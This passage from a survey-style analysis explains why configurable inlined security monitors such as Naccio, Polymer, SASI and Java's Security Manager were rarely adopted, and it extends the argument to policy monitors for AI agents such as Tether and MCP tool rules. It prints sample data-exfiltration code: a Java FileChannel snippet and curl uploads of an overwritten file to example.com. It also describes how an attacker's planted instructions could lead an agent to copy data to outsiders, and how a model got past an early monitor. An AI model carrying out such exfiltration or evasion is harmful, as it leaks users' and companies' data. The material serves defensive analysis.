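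The third premise now applies only to the people who write the platform interface. For Java, they had to define 122 resource operations and describe the library routines that affect them. *Platform Interfaces*, a page on the University of Virginia project's website, calls the process somewhat tedious and warns that errors are potential security holes. The developers wrote a tool to find the methods that can never reach native code and so need no description. It ruled out about half of the Java library, and they examined the rest by hand. At that stage they had described only part of the library, including most of the classes for files and the network.

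By October 1999 Evans considered the Java version complete enough to use against hostile programs, though it still lacked the testing an industrial product would need. The Windows version was much further behind. Describing some of the file calls had taken about two weeks, and he estimated that a skilled developer would need several months to describe the whole Windows programming interface.

That is a lot of work for a user but very little for a software company, so the effort of writing the description can't by itself explain why no vendor adopted Naccio.

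The shared description has drawbacks. An omission in the platform interface affects every policy that uses the resource, not just one. Evans acknowledged that the interface must describe several hundred routines correctly, and that Naccio's trusted computing base compares badly with most other systems'. He thought this acceptable where security needs were low or moderate, but not where security was critical. To find errors, he proposed describing Windows at two levels, the programming interface and the kernel calls beneath it, and checking whether both descriptions give the same sequence of resource operations.

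Abstraction also discards detail. Naccio's standard write operation passes on only the number of bytes, so a policy can limit how much a program writes but not what it writes. A policy author who needs the content has to extend the platform interface, which means working with the library calls that Naccio was supposed to hide.

It is hard to judge how easy Naccio was for policy authors, because Evans reports the experience of only two, himself and Twyman. Twyman wrote new policies after looking at a few examples and later built the Windows version. Evans did not think most people could do the same. Writing a policy meant writing code, and he compared the likely authors to people who write their own spreadsheet macros.

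But Naccio's designers, Evans and Twyman, expected experts to write the policies, and users to choose from a list or accept whatever their system administrator had set. They judged all but one of their sample policies general enough for a standard library. A well-stocked library would have spared ordinary users the work, so the fourth premise needs a qualification. Few users will put in the effort to get a policy of their own, but one policy can serve many of them. Someone would still have had to build the library and keep it current, and Evans left open which policy suits which environment.

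### Eighteen hundred lines for email

Polymer's email policy shows what a thorough policy looks like in a good policy language. Bauer and colleagues needed about 1,800 lines to secure mail programs that use JavaMail, a Java library for email. They assembled the policy from small parts, which Ligatti describes in more detail:

| Part | What it does |
|---|---|
| General protections | prevent misuse of class loading, reflection and system calls, and warn when memory runs low |
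| IsClientSigned | only logs and allows updates for a cryptographically signed mail program, and applies the parts below to unsigned ones |
| ConfirmAndAllowOnlyHTTP | asks the user before the program opens a web connection |
| AllowOnlyMailPorts | permits connections to the standard ports for email |
| Attachments | asks before the program creates a file of a dangerous type |
| OutgoingMail | logs each message, asks the user to confirm the recipients, sends a backup copy and adds contact details |
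| IncomingMail | logs messages, marks spam, shortens long subject lines and warns about attachments |

Other policies in the set combine these, most commonly by applying two at once and following the stricter suggestion. If the two suggest different replacement values for an action's result, neither suggestion is stricter, so Polymer blocks the action and reports an error to the program.

Even "incoming mail" took some work to define. Ligatti lists ten method patterns that can fetch a message, seven for the IMAP protocol and three for POP3. One of them is `expunge`, whose main purpose is to permanently remove deleted messages, but which also returns them to the program. Some of the methods return one message, some return several, and some return nothing and fill an array that the program supplied. Polymer lets an author handle all these cases in one abstract action, GetMail, which other policies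 can use. This is the same remedy as Naccio's platform interface, applied to a single library.

The policy author also has to list, in a separate file, every method that might matter to security, because Polymer's rewriter inserts hooks only in those methods. Java generally cannot reload its core library classes while a program runs, so an updated policy can watch only the core methods already listed. Bauer and colleagues advise policy authors to keep this in mind when they write the list.

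A policy can also interfere with itself, because Polymer checks the actions of its own policies so that no relevant action escapes. A policy that responds to an action by performing the same action will trigger itself again, possibly forever. Bauer and colleagues wrote special policies to break such loops, including one that inspects the call stack to find out whether an action came from another policy.

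The designers settled for less protection in AllowOnlyMailPorts to save effort. The policy checks the port number but ignores what the program sends, so a malicious program could send anything to a server that listens on an email port. Ligatti explains that a stronger policy could check that each connection follows an email protocol, but that this would take a lot of engineering and slow the program down.

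The Attachments policy has two gaps that Ligatti doesn't mention. It recognises dangerous files by four endings (.exe, .vbs, .hta and .mdb), but Windows also runs files that end in .bat, .com or .scr. The policy's comparison is also case-sensitive, and Windows ignores case in file names, so the policy would miss a file called `invoice.EXE`. The policy is a demonstration, and both gaps would take a minute to close. But specialists in security policies wrote it, and they were listing file types, which are far fewer than library methods.

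Even a working policy needs further changes. Ligatti observes that policies grow when engineers respond to new attacks or relax rules that proved too strict. The first version of Java confined all downloaded applets. After users objected, the next version confined only unsigned ones, so the policy also had to handle cryptographic signatures.

A policy of 1,800 lines is modest compared with the 50,000 lines of the mail client Pooka, and in principle it can serve any mail program built on JavaMail. Writing one would be feasible for a company that runs such programs for thousands of employees, but not for an individual user. Ligatti concedes that Polymer policies are too low-level for many of the people who might benefit from them, and suggests a graphical tool that would let administrators combine prepackaged policies. The email policy therefore supports the fourth premise for individuals but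 weakens it for organisations.

### Policies taken from past behaviour

Seventeen years after SASI, Erlingsson proposed no longer relying on people to write security policies. He borrowed an observation from the computer scientist Butler Lampson that a security policy is a kind of specification, a statement of what software is supposed to do. Developers are notoriously reluctant to write specifications, and often get them wrong when they have to. Erlingsson concluded that developers, administrators and users cannot be expected to define good security policies. He argued that modern programs have grown so complex that neither their developers nor their users can explain what the programs are meant to do.

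This objection is deeper than the four premises, which assume that the policy author knows what to forbid and only has trouble finding all the ways a program could do it. If Erlingsson is right, an author with a complete list of library methods would still be unsure which ones the program should call.

His alternative is to record what a program does and permit only that. In outline, it works like this:

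1. Choose a kind of event to record, such as system calls.
2. Collect the events from every run of the program, on developers' machines and on users'.
3. Permit an event if it has occurred at least *k* times in those records, where *k* is a small number that may be as low as one.
4. Stop anything else, unless someone has given explicit permission.

Windows Solitaire, for example, includes Microsoft's networking libraries but never uses them, so the resulting policy would deny it network access without anyone having to think of this. Erlingsson's second example is a Linux flaw, disclosed in 2016, that could be exploited through the keyctl system call. Commonly used applications had never made that call, so a policy based on their history would have blocked the attack.

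Earlier researchers had tried a similar approach, called anomaly detection. They recorded a program's behaviour during a training period and treated later departures from it as suspicious. A short training period misses many rare but legitimate behaviours, so these systems raised many false alarms. Erlingsson's answer is to record many more runs. A popular program runs billions of times, and if the records cover all its runs, including the developers' tests, even rare behaviour should appear in them.

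Several weaknesses remain, most of which he raises himself. A new program has no past runs on which to base a policy. Some code runs only at the end of the year, or in a configuration that no tester tried. Each update can add legitimate behaviour that the old records lack, so developers would have to publish a new policy with every update. Developers also do things that users should not be able to do. The mail server sendmail once had a debugging command that attackers could exploit, and a policy based on developers' runs might have permitted it. Collecting detailed records from users' computers also raises privacy problems.

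Programs that contain an interpreter are especially hard to write policies for. A word processor that runs macros can do almost anything a macro's author wants, so over enough runs its history may include nearly every possible event. A policy drawn from that history would forbid very little.

The simplest version of the method also can't express SASI's example. Erlingsson expects practical systems to record which events occur but not their order. A mail program reads files and sends messages every day, so both events are in its history, and the policy would permit a message that leaks a file the program has just read. Deriving a policy from behaviour saves the author work, but the policy reflects what is usual, so someone still has to write a rule that forbids a harmful combination of ordinary actions.

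### Rules for AI agents

Writing a complete policy seems easier for AI agents, because a developer normally gives an agent a list of named tools that is often short enough to read in full. If we again assume, for illustration, a 99% chance of classifying each tool correctly, the chance of classifying all 20 tools in a list correctly is 82%, compared with 13% for the 200 methods. A general-purpose tool such as a shell removes this advantage, because the policy must again cover every route the operating system offers.

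For agents with specific tools, most of the remaining work is defining what the rules mean. The one-line rule against leaks in Palumbo and colleagues' system, FORGE (first circulated as PCAS), works only if someone has specified which tools send data outside and which data are sensitive. Suppose an agent has a calendar tool that emails an invitation to everyone on the guest list. If the developer thinks of it as a scheduling tool and doesn't mark it as an external send, the rule never applies to it, and the agent can leak a document in the text of an invitation. These classifications serve the same purpose as Naccio's platform interface, and in both systems one wrong entry weakens every rule that relies on it.

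Newer systems try to reduce how much policy developers have to write. FORGE and NOMOS translate written rules into checks, and Sapien uses policies with parts that are filled in at run time. Sapien's approach suits agents because a developer can't know in advance which file or recipient a user's task will involve. For example, a rule could allow email only to a recipient named in the user's request. Whatever supplies the missing values becomes part of the trusted computing base. If a document the agent reads can influence those values, an attacker could use it to set that part of the policy.

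Language models can take over much of the drafting. In seconds, a model can produce a long list of the Java methods that read files, and the list may well include some that a specialist would forget. Reviewing the list is also easier than writing it. At a minute per entry, 200 entries take a little over three hours. But this review finds only the entries that shouldn't be there. A reviewer can notice that a method is missing only if they already know about it, which is the third premise again.

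Evans's proposal to describe Windows twice suggests a partial remedy. If two drafts each miss 1% of the 200 methods, independently of each other, the chance that both miss a given method is one in 10,000, and the combined list is complete 98% of the time. Two drafts from the same model are unlikely to be independent, because the model may well omit the same method both times. Omissions should coincide less often if the developer combines drafts from different models, or checks a draft against a record of which native methods the library calls.

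Translation is also limited when the original rule is vague. "Email customers only when necessary" has no single correct translation until someone decides what counts as necessary. A model will produce a precise check anyway, and that check may define "necessary" in a way that nobody at the company intended. This mistake is easier to notice in examples than in code. For example, someone who knows the business but not the policy language can review ten emails that the check would allow and ten that it would block.

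For developers who can't be sure their lists are complete, the safer default is to permit named tools and block the rest, an option that SASI also had. This is practical with 20 tools, but it was not for a Java program with thousands of library methods. If the developer leaves out a tool the agent needs, the agent can't finish its task, and the user is likely to report the failure.

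## Dependence on a platform that changes

A complete policy can become incomplete without anyone editing it. Policies identify events by details of a platform, such as a Java method's name, a Windows library function or a pattern of machine instructions, and the platform's developers change these details. Anyone who adopts a configurable monitor must therefore maintain its policy as well as write it. If this is a real cause of low adoption, few organisations would accept that upkeep for a protection they rarely see at work.

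### Silent gaps and broken programs

Let *E* be the set of events that a platform offers and *N* the events that a policy names. A monitor needs a default for the events in *E* but not in *N*, which it either permits or blocks. Now suppose that a new release of the platform adds a set of events *A*. No rule mentions them, so the default decides what happens:

- If the monitor permits whatever the policy doesn't name, a program can use *A* to do what the policy should prevent. Nothing crashes, and the monitor reports nothing.
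- If the monitor blocks whatever the policy doesn't name, a harmless program stops working once its developers start using *A*.

Users soon report a broken program, but a silent gap may last until an attacker or an auditor finds it. Other changes to the platform cause similar trouble:

| Change in the platform | Unnamed events permitted | Unnamed events blocked |
|---|---|---|
| a new call appears | the call escapes the policy | programs that use it stop working |
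| a new call replaces a named one | the old rule no longer matches anything | programs that switch to the new call stop working |
| a named call gains a new effect | the old rule may permit the new effect | the same |

The default makes no difference in the last row, because the policy does name the call.

The Windows version of Naccio offered both defaults. Twyman (1999), in *Flexible Code Safety for Win32*, explains that whoever described a Windows library could let its unlisted functions through or redirect them to a function that reports a violation. Three lines from his prototype show the choices:

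```
DeleteFileA = wrapper_DeleteFileA
MulDiv      = KERNEL32.MulDiv
DeleteFileW = NACCLIB.IllegalAPIViolation
```

The first line sends calls to a checked version of the function, and the second lets a harmless arithmetic function through. DeleteFileW does the same job as DeleteFileA but takes the file name in Unicode, which the prototype couldn't handle, so Twyman blocked it. A program that used DeleteFileW to remove its own temporary file would trigger a violation. If the default had been to allow such calls, any program could have used DeleteFileW to delete any file the user could.

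### Java's second set of file and network calls

In 2002 Java 1.4 added a second way to reach files and the network, a package called java.nio ("new I/O"). *JSR 51* (2002), from the Java Community Process, which approves changes to Java, dates the specification's final release to 9 May 2002. O'Reilly's *New I/O Package* explains that the package's designers introduced two new concepts, channels and buffers. A channel is a connection to a file or a socket, and a buffer holds the data that passes through it. The designers did not build the package on Java's older streams.

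This program sends a file over the network without using either of the methods that SASI's example policy names:

```
FileChannel in = new FileInputStream("secrets.txt").getChannel();
ByteBuffer data = in.map(FileChannel.MapMode.READ_ONLY, 0, in.size());

SocketChannel out = SocketChannel.open(
    new InetSocketAddress("example.com", 80));
out.write(data);
```

The automaton therefore stays in its start state, and the file leaves the machine.

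Even a complete list of the methods that read files in 1999 would not have caught the program. Adding the new `FileChannel.read` to the list would not help either, because the program never calls a read method. It calls `map`, which makes the file part of the program's memory, and the operating system fetches the contents when the program accesses that memory. Checks on the native methods beneath the old classes would also miss it, because the new classes have their own native methods.

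A rule about opening files would have worked for longer. In Java 1.4 a program could get a file's channel only after opening the file with one of the older classes. Java 7 removed that requirement in 2011 by adding `FileChannel.open` and `Files.readAllBytes`, which don't need the older classes. Checking when a file is opened is also less precise than checking when it is read or written. Twyman found that the compression program pkzip asks for write access to files that it only reads, so two of his policies blocked legitimate work. He had to move their checks from opening a file to writing to it, which made them slower.

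A policy permitting only methods that existed in 1999 would have had the opposite problem. One purpose of java.nio was to let a server handle many connections without a separate thread for each. If developers had switched a web server to java.nio for this reason, the policy would have stopped it from working, even though the switch did not change which pages it served or to whom.

Sun Microsystems (2002) also documented new behaviour in the existing socket classes, including revised `connect` and `close` methods. In 2019 Java 13 replaced the code beneath ordinary sockets, so their output streams no longer belonged to the `SocketOutputStream` class named in SASI's policy. After that, even a rule that tested for the class at run time would never have matched.

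### One compiler's habits

Java bytecode at least contains the names of methods, but the x86 version of SASI had to work with whatever code gcc, the GNU C compiler, produced. Erlingsson and Schneider relied on that code to behave the same after they inserted extra instructions, and to jump only to places that gcc had labelled.

Erlingsson and Schneider also relied on gcc's use of the register `%ebp` to hold an address in the stack, the memory where functions keep their local variables. Because that address was always valid, their rewriter left out memory checks for accesses through `%ebp`. This saved a lot of time and kept their speed comparison with MiSFIT fair, since MiSFIT made the same assumption. They nevertheless called it a questionable trade-off because it made gcc part of the trusted computing base.

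Since version 4.6, released in 2011, gcc has by default used `%ebp` for ordinary data, instead of reserving it for the frame pointer, when optimising 32-bit Linux programs for speed. The register can then hold any value, including an address outside the program's permitted memory, and SASI's rewriter would not check writes through it.

Function calls, which a policy had to recognise by their instruction sequences, depended on the compiler as well. Suppose that a function does nothing but pass its one argument on to `send_message`. A compiler might produce this:

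```
pushl 4(%esp)        ; copy the argument
call  send_message
addl  $4, %esp       ; discard the copy
ret
```

An optimising compiler can replace all four instructions with one:

```
jmp   send_message   ; the argument is already in place
```

Both versions send the same message, but a policy that looks for a `call` instruction misses the second. A policy author could add a rule for the jump and then one for each further optimisation, but would have to repeat the work for any other compiler.

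Rewriting the C++ source instead would have made functions easy to find, but Erlingsson and Schneider rejected it because it would have added the C++ compiler to the trusted computing base. They preferred compiled code that carries simple, checkable annotations about functions and types. Java bytecode already had these, so they based their next system on it.

### Calls whose target depends on the object

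The method named in a bytecode instruction is not always the one that runs. Vanoverberghe and Piessens dealt with this in a .NET bytecode rewriter that inserts checks around the application's calls to the library.

Polymer puts its checks inside the library methods instead, so they run no matter how the program reaches those methods. But this requires changing the platform's libraries, which may be in a phone's read-only memory. It also makes it harder to treat a call from the application differently from the same call by another part of the library. Vanoverberghe and Piessens therefore left the libraries unchanged, and had to block several ways for programs to bypass their checks.

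One route around the monitor is the `InputStream.read()` call that defeats SASI's example. Vanoverberghe and Piessens close it by requiring any policy that lists a subclass's version of a method to list the parent class's version too. Their rewriter then inserts a test of the object's actual class. In SASI's example, the file check would then run when the object is a `FileInputStream` but not when the program reads from the keyboard.

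An application can also define its own subclass of a library class and inherit a monitored method. A call through the subclass then names a class that the policy's author did not know about. The rewriter does not allow such inheritance. Instead, the application has to define the method itself and call the library's version explicitly so that the rewriter can detect the call. Vanoverberghe and Piessens note that a tool could make this change automatically.

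Delegates, which are .NET objects that hold references to one or more methods, are harder to handle. Calling a delegate runs all of its methods. A program can fill a delegate in one place and call it in another, so the rewriter cannot tell from the call which methods will run. Instead, where the application takes a reference to a monitored method, the rewriter substitutes a reference to a small wrapper that contains the checks.

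Vanoverberghe and Piessens argue that, with these fixes, every monitored call gets its checks. Their argument starts from a proof for a simplified model of .NET that leaves out interfaces and multithreading. They also assume that the library never passes the application a delegate that points to a monitored method. This was true of the methods they had considered, but a later release of the library could make it false. A release could also add a subclass that overrides a monitored method, and the old class tests would not detect it. The guarantee therefore holds for one version of the platform, and someone has to recheck the assumptions and regenerate the tests for the next.

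The real .NET virtual machine added further complications. For example, it doesn't let a program enter an error-handling block while intermediate values are still on its evaluation stack. The inserted checks need such blocks, so the rewriter has to save the values and restore them afterwards. Vanoverberghe and Piessens solved these problems and ran the rewriter on real applications with little overhead, which suggests specialists can manage the difficulties.

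### Hardening that removed a protection

A rewriter can also damage a defence that its developers did not intend to change. In *Too Subtle to Notice* (2025), Ye and Hu tested 21 security tools that work as inlined monitors or help to build them. Eleven gave every program they processed an executable stack.

An executable stack undoes one of the most successful defences against memory attacks. Attackers used to send a vulnerable program more data than a buffer on the stack could hold. The excess contained machine code and overwrote the current function's return address, so the program jumped to the attacker's code. Modern systems prevent this by making each page of memory either writable or executable, but not both. The stack has to be writable, so the processor won't run code there. Attackers must then piece together fragments of the program's existing code, which is much more laborious.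 A program with an executable stack is vulnerable to the old attack again, unless another defence stops it.

The mistake comes from a convention in Linux's compilation tools. Some old programs need to run code on the stack, so the tools assume that a file of machine code might need this unless it contains an empty section called `.note.GNU-stack`. Compilers add the section automatically. Programmers who write assembly code by hand have to add this line themselves:

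```
.section .note.GNU-stack,"",@progbits
```

A single file without the line makes the whole program's stack executable. Ye and Hu demonstrate this with a harmless C program and an assembly file, `a.s`, that contains nothing at all:

| Command | Stack permissions |
|---|---|
| `gcc hello_world.c` | read, write |
| `gcc hello_world.c a.s` | read, write, execute |

Inlined monitors often include assembly code. All 11 affected tools were among the 15 that use assembly files. Four of the 11 enforce control-flow integrity, two isolate parts of a program from each other, and five are binary rewriters, which turn a compiled program into assembly, let a developer add checks and then reassemble it. The six tools that don't use assembly files were unaffected. They include LLVM's CFI, Android's kernel CFI and the WebAssembly runtime Wasmtime, which come from the families of monitors that reached production.

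The damage varied by tool. PathArmor checks only the last 16 indirect jumps, calls and returns before a sensitive system call, so an attacker could run code on the stack first and then arrange 16 that look legitimate. ERIM uses special processor instructions to control access to protected memory, and an attacker could put those instructions on the stack. In Donky, no code used the executable stack, so the risk was small. Seven of the 11 tools now have a fix, but PathArmor won't get one because nobody maintains it.

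The stack convention was older than all 21 tools, so this finding mainly shows how easily experts overlook a platform detail. A second finding is closer to platform change. Ye and Hu report that every tool that made the stack executable also switched off Intel CET, a hardware defence against hijacked jumps and returns. Linux enables CET only if every file in the program declares support for it, and the tools' assembly files didn't. Five of the affected tools appeared before Intel announced CET in 2016, so their developers couldn't have known to declare support for it.

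### Updates and signatures

Developers often sign their programs so that a device can detect any change to the files. Inserting even one check changes a file, so the signature no longer matches. Whoever rewrites the program can sign it again with another key, but the device must then trust that key, and the new signature doesn't show that the code came from the developer.

This work has to be repeated for every update. Android, for instance, normally rejects an update whose signing key differs from the installed app's, so a rewritten app can't receive the developer's updates directly. Someone has to obtain, rewrite, sign and distribute each one. Polymer avoids changing an application's files by rewriting its classes as they load, but this works only where the platform lets other software alter code after the signature has been checked. Apple's iPhones don't allow this.

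Without signatures, an update can cause either of the two failures. Twyman's rewriter keeps the program's original file name, so an automatic update could overwrite the rewritten program with an unmonitored one that would work normally. If the update only added a new library, the monitored program would report a violation when it tried to load that library. The user would have to run the rewriter again and specify the new library.

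Rewriting seldom seems to break the program itself. Erlingsson and Schneider were pleasantly surprised that the code they inserted did not affect the program's correctness. They credited high-level languages, which keep programmers from relying on the exact position of code and data.

### How far typed code, stable interfaces and regeneration help

Good engineering can remove only some of these difficulties. Typed bytecode makes events much easier to recognise, since a rewriter for Java doesn't need to guess what a function call looks like. But when java.nio was added to Java, the types showed only that a program called `FileChannel.map`, not that the call could reveal a file's contents.

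A stable interface also helps. Twyman placed Naccio's checks at the documented Windows programming interface instead of the undocumented kernel calls of Windows NT. He argued that one description could then serve several versions of the library, with small corrections where they differ, because only the behaviour of the library's functions matters. Rules for old calls then stay valid, so old programs stay covered. However, developers usually keep an interface stable by not removing calls, and they can still add new ones.

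Tools can automate part of the remaining work. They can rewrite each new version of a program, compare two releases of a library and list the new methods that reach native code. Someone still has to decide what each method does. As an illustration, suppose that each release adds ten relevant methods and that the policy's maintainer again has a 99% chance of classifying each one correctly. A policy that starts out complete is still complete after five releases with probability

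$$0.99^{50} \approx 0.61.$$

Fixed-policy monitors largely avoid this decay. CFI checks indirect calls regardless of which function they lead to, so a new library function needs no new rule, and the compiler regenerates the checks at every build. WebAssembly goes further, because a module can reach files or the network only through functions that the surrounding program passes to it. The module can't use a new operating-system call until someone chooses to provide it.

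The pattern of adoption therefore fits this cause fairly well, but the timing does not. Java 1.4 came out two years after the last update to Naccio's home page, so java.nio can't explain why so few people had adopted Naccio by then. At most, potential users may have foreseen the upkeep and stayed away, but there is no record of anyone giving that reason. The best direct evidence concerns x86 SASI, whose designers blamed the difficulty of finding events in compiled code.

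### File tools and shell commands

An agent with specific tools gives its monitor clearer events than a Java program does, because each tool call includes the files and hosts involved. For example, a company might want to keep its inventory file from leaving the machine while its agent has the tools `copy_file(source, target)` and `upload_file(path, host)`. The monitor can mark the file as sensitive, extend the mark to every copy the agent makes, and block uploads of anything marked.

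With a shell tool, every event becomes `run(command)`, where the command is a string of text. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, illustrate the difficulty with three commands much like these:

```
curl -T report.txt https://example.com/    # 1
cp inventory.csv report.txt                # 2
curl -T report.txt https://example.com/    # 3
```

The first command uploads a harmless report. The second overwrites the report with the company's inventory, and the third uploads the overwritten file. The first and third commands are identical, so no rule that judges each command by its text alone can allow one and block the other. The text may also reveal very little about what a command does, as when it runs a Python script that makes its own network requests.

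Tether therefore runs each command before deciding whether to permit its effects:

1. It starts the command in a temporary layer over the file system, so that changes don't reach the real files.
2. It records the system calls that the command makes, and a proxy holds any outgoing network request.
3. It translates these records into 11 kinds of abstract action, such as reading, copying and uploading.
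4. It checks the actions against the policy and updates the security labels on files.
5. It keeps the changes and releases the requests if the policy permits everything, and otherwise discards them.

In the example, the copy gives `report.txt` the inventory's "sensitive" label, and Tether blocks the second upload. System calls don't show exactly which data went where, so if a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as if it contained data from the first.

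Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded runs of coding agents from two benchmarks, some harmless and some containing an attack. They compared Tether with Auto Mode, a feature of Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code in which a second language model reviews commands:

| Monitor | Attacks blocked | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 of 344 | 74 of 1,590 (4.7%) |
| Auto Mode, default rules | 315 of 344 (91.6%) | 155 of 1,590 (9.7%) |
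| Auto Mode, given Tether's policy | 307 of 344 (89.2%) | 55 of 1,590 (3.5%) |

Most of Tether's false alarms, 50 of the 74, came from unrequested edits to protected files. Another 17 came from commands such as `grep -r`, which searches every file in a directory. Tether records that the command opened a secret file but can't detect whether the agent meant to open it.

The perfect score covers only runs whose every action Tether can trace and model. It excludes runs with background processes or database queries, although a stricter policy can block these actions outright. Sistla and colleagues also judge that no formal monitor could handle 28.2% of the runs in one benchmark and 22.1% in the other, because recognising an attack in them requires understanding content, such as malicious code in a file that the agent is allowed to edit. They refined the policy on traces from the benchmarks, so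 false alarms could be more common on unfamiliar tasks.

Tether moves the dependence on the platform out of the policy and into a separate component, which maps system calls to abstract actions such as uploads and copies. The policy's rules refer to these actions, much as Naccio's rules refer to abstract resources. Sistla and colleagues used the proof assistant Lean to prove, among other guarantees, that their policy keeps secret data out of the agent's context. The proofs start from the abstract actions, so they do not cover system calls that the mapping misses. An early version had such gaps. A language model that tried to get past it succeeded 40% of the time, partly because Tether did not track hard links, which give one file a second name. After two rounds of fixes, the rate fell to zero.

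Linux has also had a counterpart to java.nio since 2019, an interface called io_uring. It lets a program place requests in memory shared with the kernel, so the program can read files without the usual read calls that Tether records. Tether blocks io_uring entirely to avoid missing these reads, but programs that depend on io_uring can't run normally under Tether.

### Tool definitions that change

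Even typed tools change. Many agents get theirs through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. The agent's harness requests a list of tools from an MCP server, with each tool's name, description and accepted arguments. The server can send notice of a new list during a session. The protocol doesn't limit how often this may happen, and the server's operator may not know about the policies that depend on its tools.

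Suppose that a company lets its agent call `send_email` only when the `to` argument is a company address. The server's operator then adds an optional argument, `cc`:

```
"properties": {
  "to":      {"type": "string"},
  "subject": {"type": "string"},
  "body":    {"type": "string"},
  "cc":      {"type": "string"}
}
```

The rule still matches the tool and checks `to`, but an attacker who has planted instructions in a document can now make the agent copy an outsider on a message to a colleague. A policy that rejects any argument it doesn't name stops this attack, but it also blocks every legitimate email that copies in a second colleague.

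Silent gaps open faster with agents than they did with Java. Existing Java programs didn't use java.nio until a programmer changed them, which gave policy authors some time to catch up. A language model reads the current tool definitions and may use a new argument in its next task. Blocking also does less harm with agents, because an agent can often drop the new argument or use an older tool. Both differences strengthen the case for blocking whatever the policy doesn't name.

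A harness can enforce this by storing a cryptographic hash of each tool definition when someone reviews it, and blocking the tool if the hash changes. Every edit then needs a new review, even a typo fix in a description. Leaving descriptions out of the hash would be risky, because the model reads them and an attacker could hide instructions there.

The hash doesn't cover the server's code. A `save_note` tool could start publishing its notes on a public web page while its definition stayed the same. Tether detects hidden effects by tracing what a command does on the agent's machine, but it can't trace system calls on a server that someone else runs.

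## Permission checks built into the runtime

A company that wanted to restrict Java programs in 1999 didn't need a rewriter, because Java already came with the Security Manager, which could stop a program from opening a file or a network connection. Microsoft's .NET followed in 2002 with a similar system, Code Access Security. Both were free, and the makers of the runtimes maintained them. But few people who wanted to restrict programs used these built-in checks, which is evidence against the idea that inlined monitors saw little adoption because runtimes already offered an alternative.

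### How the Security Manager decides

According to OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), the proposal to remove the Security Manager, its earliest rules restricted only applets, the small programs that web pages loaded into a browser, and let local programs do anything. Java 1.2, released in December 1998, replaced this division with permissions. All code started out untrusted, and users granted each body of code the permissions it needed.

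Sun's engineers wrote the checks into Java's own libraries by hand. The code that opens a file for reading, for example, contains lines like these:

```
SecurityManager security = System.getSecurityManager();
if (security != null) {
    security.checkRead(name);   // throws an exception if not permitted
}
```

If nobody has switched the Security Manager on, the test in the second line fails and the program carries on unchecked. If it is on, it consults a policy file with entries such as this one, which lets the code in `report.jar` read anything under `/data`:

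```
grant codeBase "file:/app/report.jar" {
    permission java.io.FilePermission "/data/-", "read";
};
```

The Security Manager doesn't consider only the code that asked for the file. It inspects the whole call stack, the chain of methods that have started but not yet finished. Suppose that the stack holds the methods *f*₁ (the oldest) to *f*ₙ (the most recent), and that *P*(*f*) is the set of permissions for the code that contains *f*. An action that needs permission *p* may go ahead only if

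$$p \in P(f_1) \cap P(f_2) \cap \dots \cap P(f_n).$$

The .NET system also inspects the stack. Microsoft's *Code Access Security* explains that this guards against luring attacks, in which less trusted code calls highly trusted code to do something forbidden. For example, a game without permission to write files could call a trusted report library to overwrite one. A check on the library alone would allow this, but stack inspection also checks the game and blocks the write.

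This rule also blocks harmless work. Mullan and Buckley, in *JEP 486*, the later proposal that disabled the Security Manager, give the example of a program that may not read files but asks Java for the local time. To answer, Java has to read its own time-zone file. The library therefore asserts its privileges by making the request inside a call to `doPrivileged`. If *f*ₖ is the most recent method to have done this, the Security Manager checks only *f*ₖ to *f*ₙ and ignores older callers:

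| Call stack, oldest first | May read the time-zone file? | Checked without the assertion | Checked with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| the program | no | yes | no |
| Java's time library | yes | yes | yes |
| Java's file library | yes | yes | yes |
| *Result* | | *denied* | *allowed* |

The assertion is safe here because the program can't choose which file the library reads. A library that asserted its privileges to open any file its caller named would make luring attacks possible again.

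Stack inspection doesn't cover methods that have already returned, including one that has just read a file, so no policy file can express SASI's rule "no messages sent after reading a file". A programmer could write a custom Security Manager that remembered file reads and then refused new connections. It still couldn't stop a send over a connection that was already open, because Java checks permission when a program connects and not each time it writes. Inlined monitors could enforce such rules, so the runtime's built-in checks did not make them technically redundant.

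### Who used it

Applets ran under the Security Manager without their users having to write a policy. Outside the browser, it was off by default. According to OpenJDK, a handful of applications and frameworks shipped with a policy file, including Elasticsearch and Tomcat (a web server for Java programs). Mullan and Buckley call use of the Security Manager exceedingly rare and say that, in their experience, most of the few applications that enabled it "blindly grant all permissions to their code".

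Neither proposal includes a count of users, and both come from people who had to maintain the Security Manager and wanted to stop. Their best evidence is that companies upgraded in large numbers after Java 17 began to print warnings in 2021, yet Mullan and Buckley saw hardly any discussion of the warnings. A company that depended on the Security Manager might have stayed on an older version and never seen a warning, which weakens this evidence. But people who opposed the removal also say most developers gave up on policy files.

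The Security Manager protected ordinary users by default when it enforced a built-in policy for applets, but hardly anyone used it when each developer had to write a policy. This is an unusually close comparison between fixed and configurable policies, because the language and runtime were the same and many of the checks were in the same places. It isn't perfect, because applets came from strangers and most server programs did not, so the need for protection differed too.

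### Why developers avoided it

The Security Manager didn't support partial policies. A developer who only wanted to restrict a program's file reads to `/data` could write the entry shown above, but the program then couldn't write its log or connect to its database, because the policy didn't grant those permissions. The policy language couldn't express "everything except reading other files", so the developer had to find and list every permission the program needed.

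Permissions also spread from libraries to the applications that call them. Suppose that a library for making PDFs reads fonts from a system directory. The application is on the stack when this happens, so it needs permission to read the fonts as well, even though its own code never touches them. If *L* is the set of libraries that don't assert their privileges, the application needs

$$P_{\text{app}} \supseteq \bigcup_{\ell \in L} P_\ell,$$

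where *P*ₗ is what library ℓ needs. An application with 30 such libraries has to hold the permissions of all 30, and a flaw in the application's own code can misuse any of them. A library's developer can prevent this with careful calls to `doPrivileged`, but OpenJDK considers the necessary rules far beyond most developers' interest. The easiest remedy was to grant `AllPermission`, which includes every permission and removes most of the benefit.

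*Security and Sandboxing Post SecurityManager* (2021), a post on Inside Java by a member of Oracle's Java team, also describes permissions as hard to maintain. The permissions an application needs depend on the internal workings of its libraries, so someone has to work them out again after every update. Programs that pass work between threads need additional code, because the second thread's stack doesn't include the code that requested the work. OpenJDK also cites slow permission checks as a reason for the decision to leave the Security Manager off.

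The Security Manager also created work for Java's maintainers. Over 1,000 methods had to check permissions, and over 1,200 had to raise their privileges, as the time library does. Every change to these methods needed a security review, whether or not anyone used the Security Manager. Mullan and Buckley counted about 4,000 tests for it and expected to delete over 50,000 lines of code, including tests. In a December 2024 summary on Inside Java, the Java team's news site, Oracle listed maintenance as one of four reasons for the removal, along with complexity, limited adoption and a change in threats.

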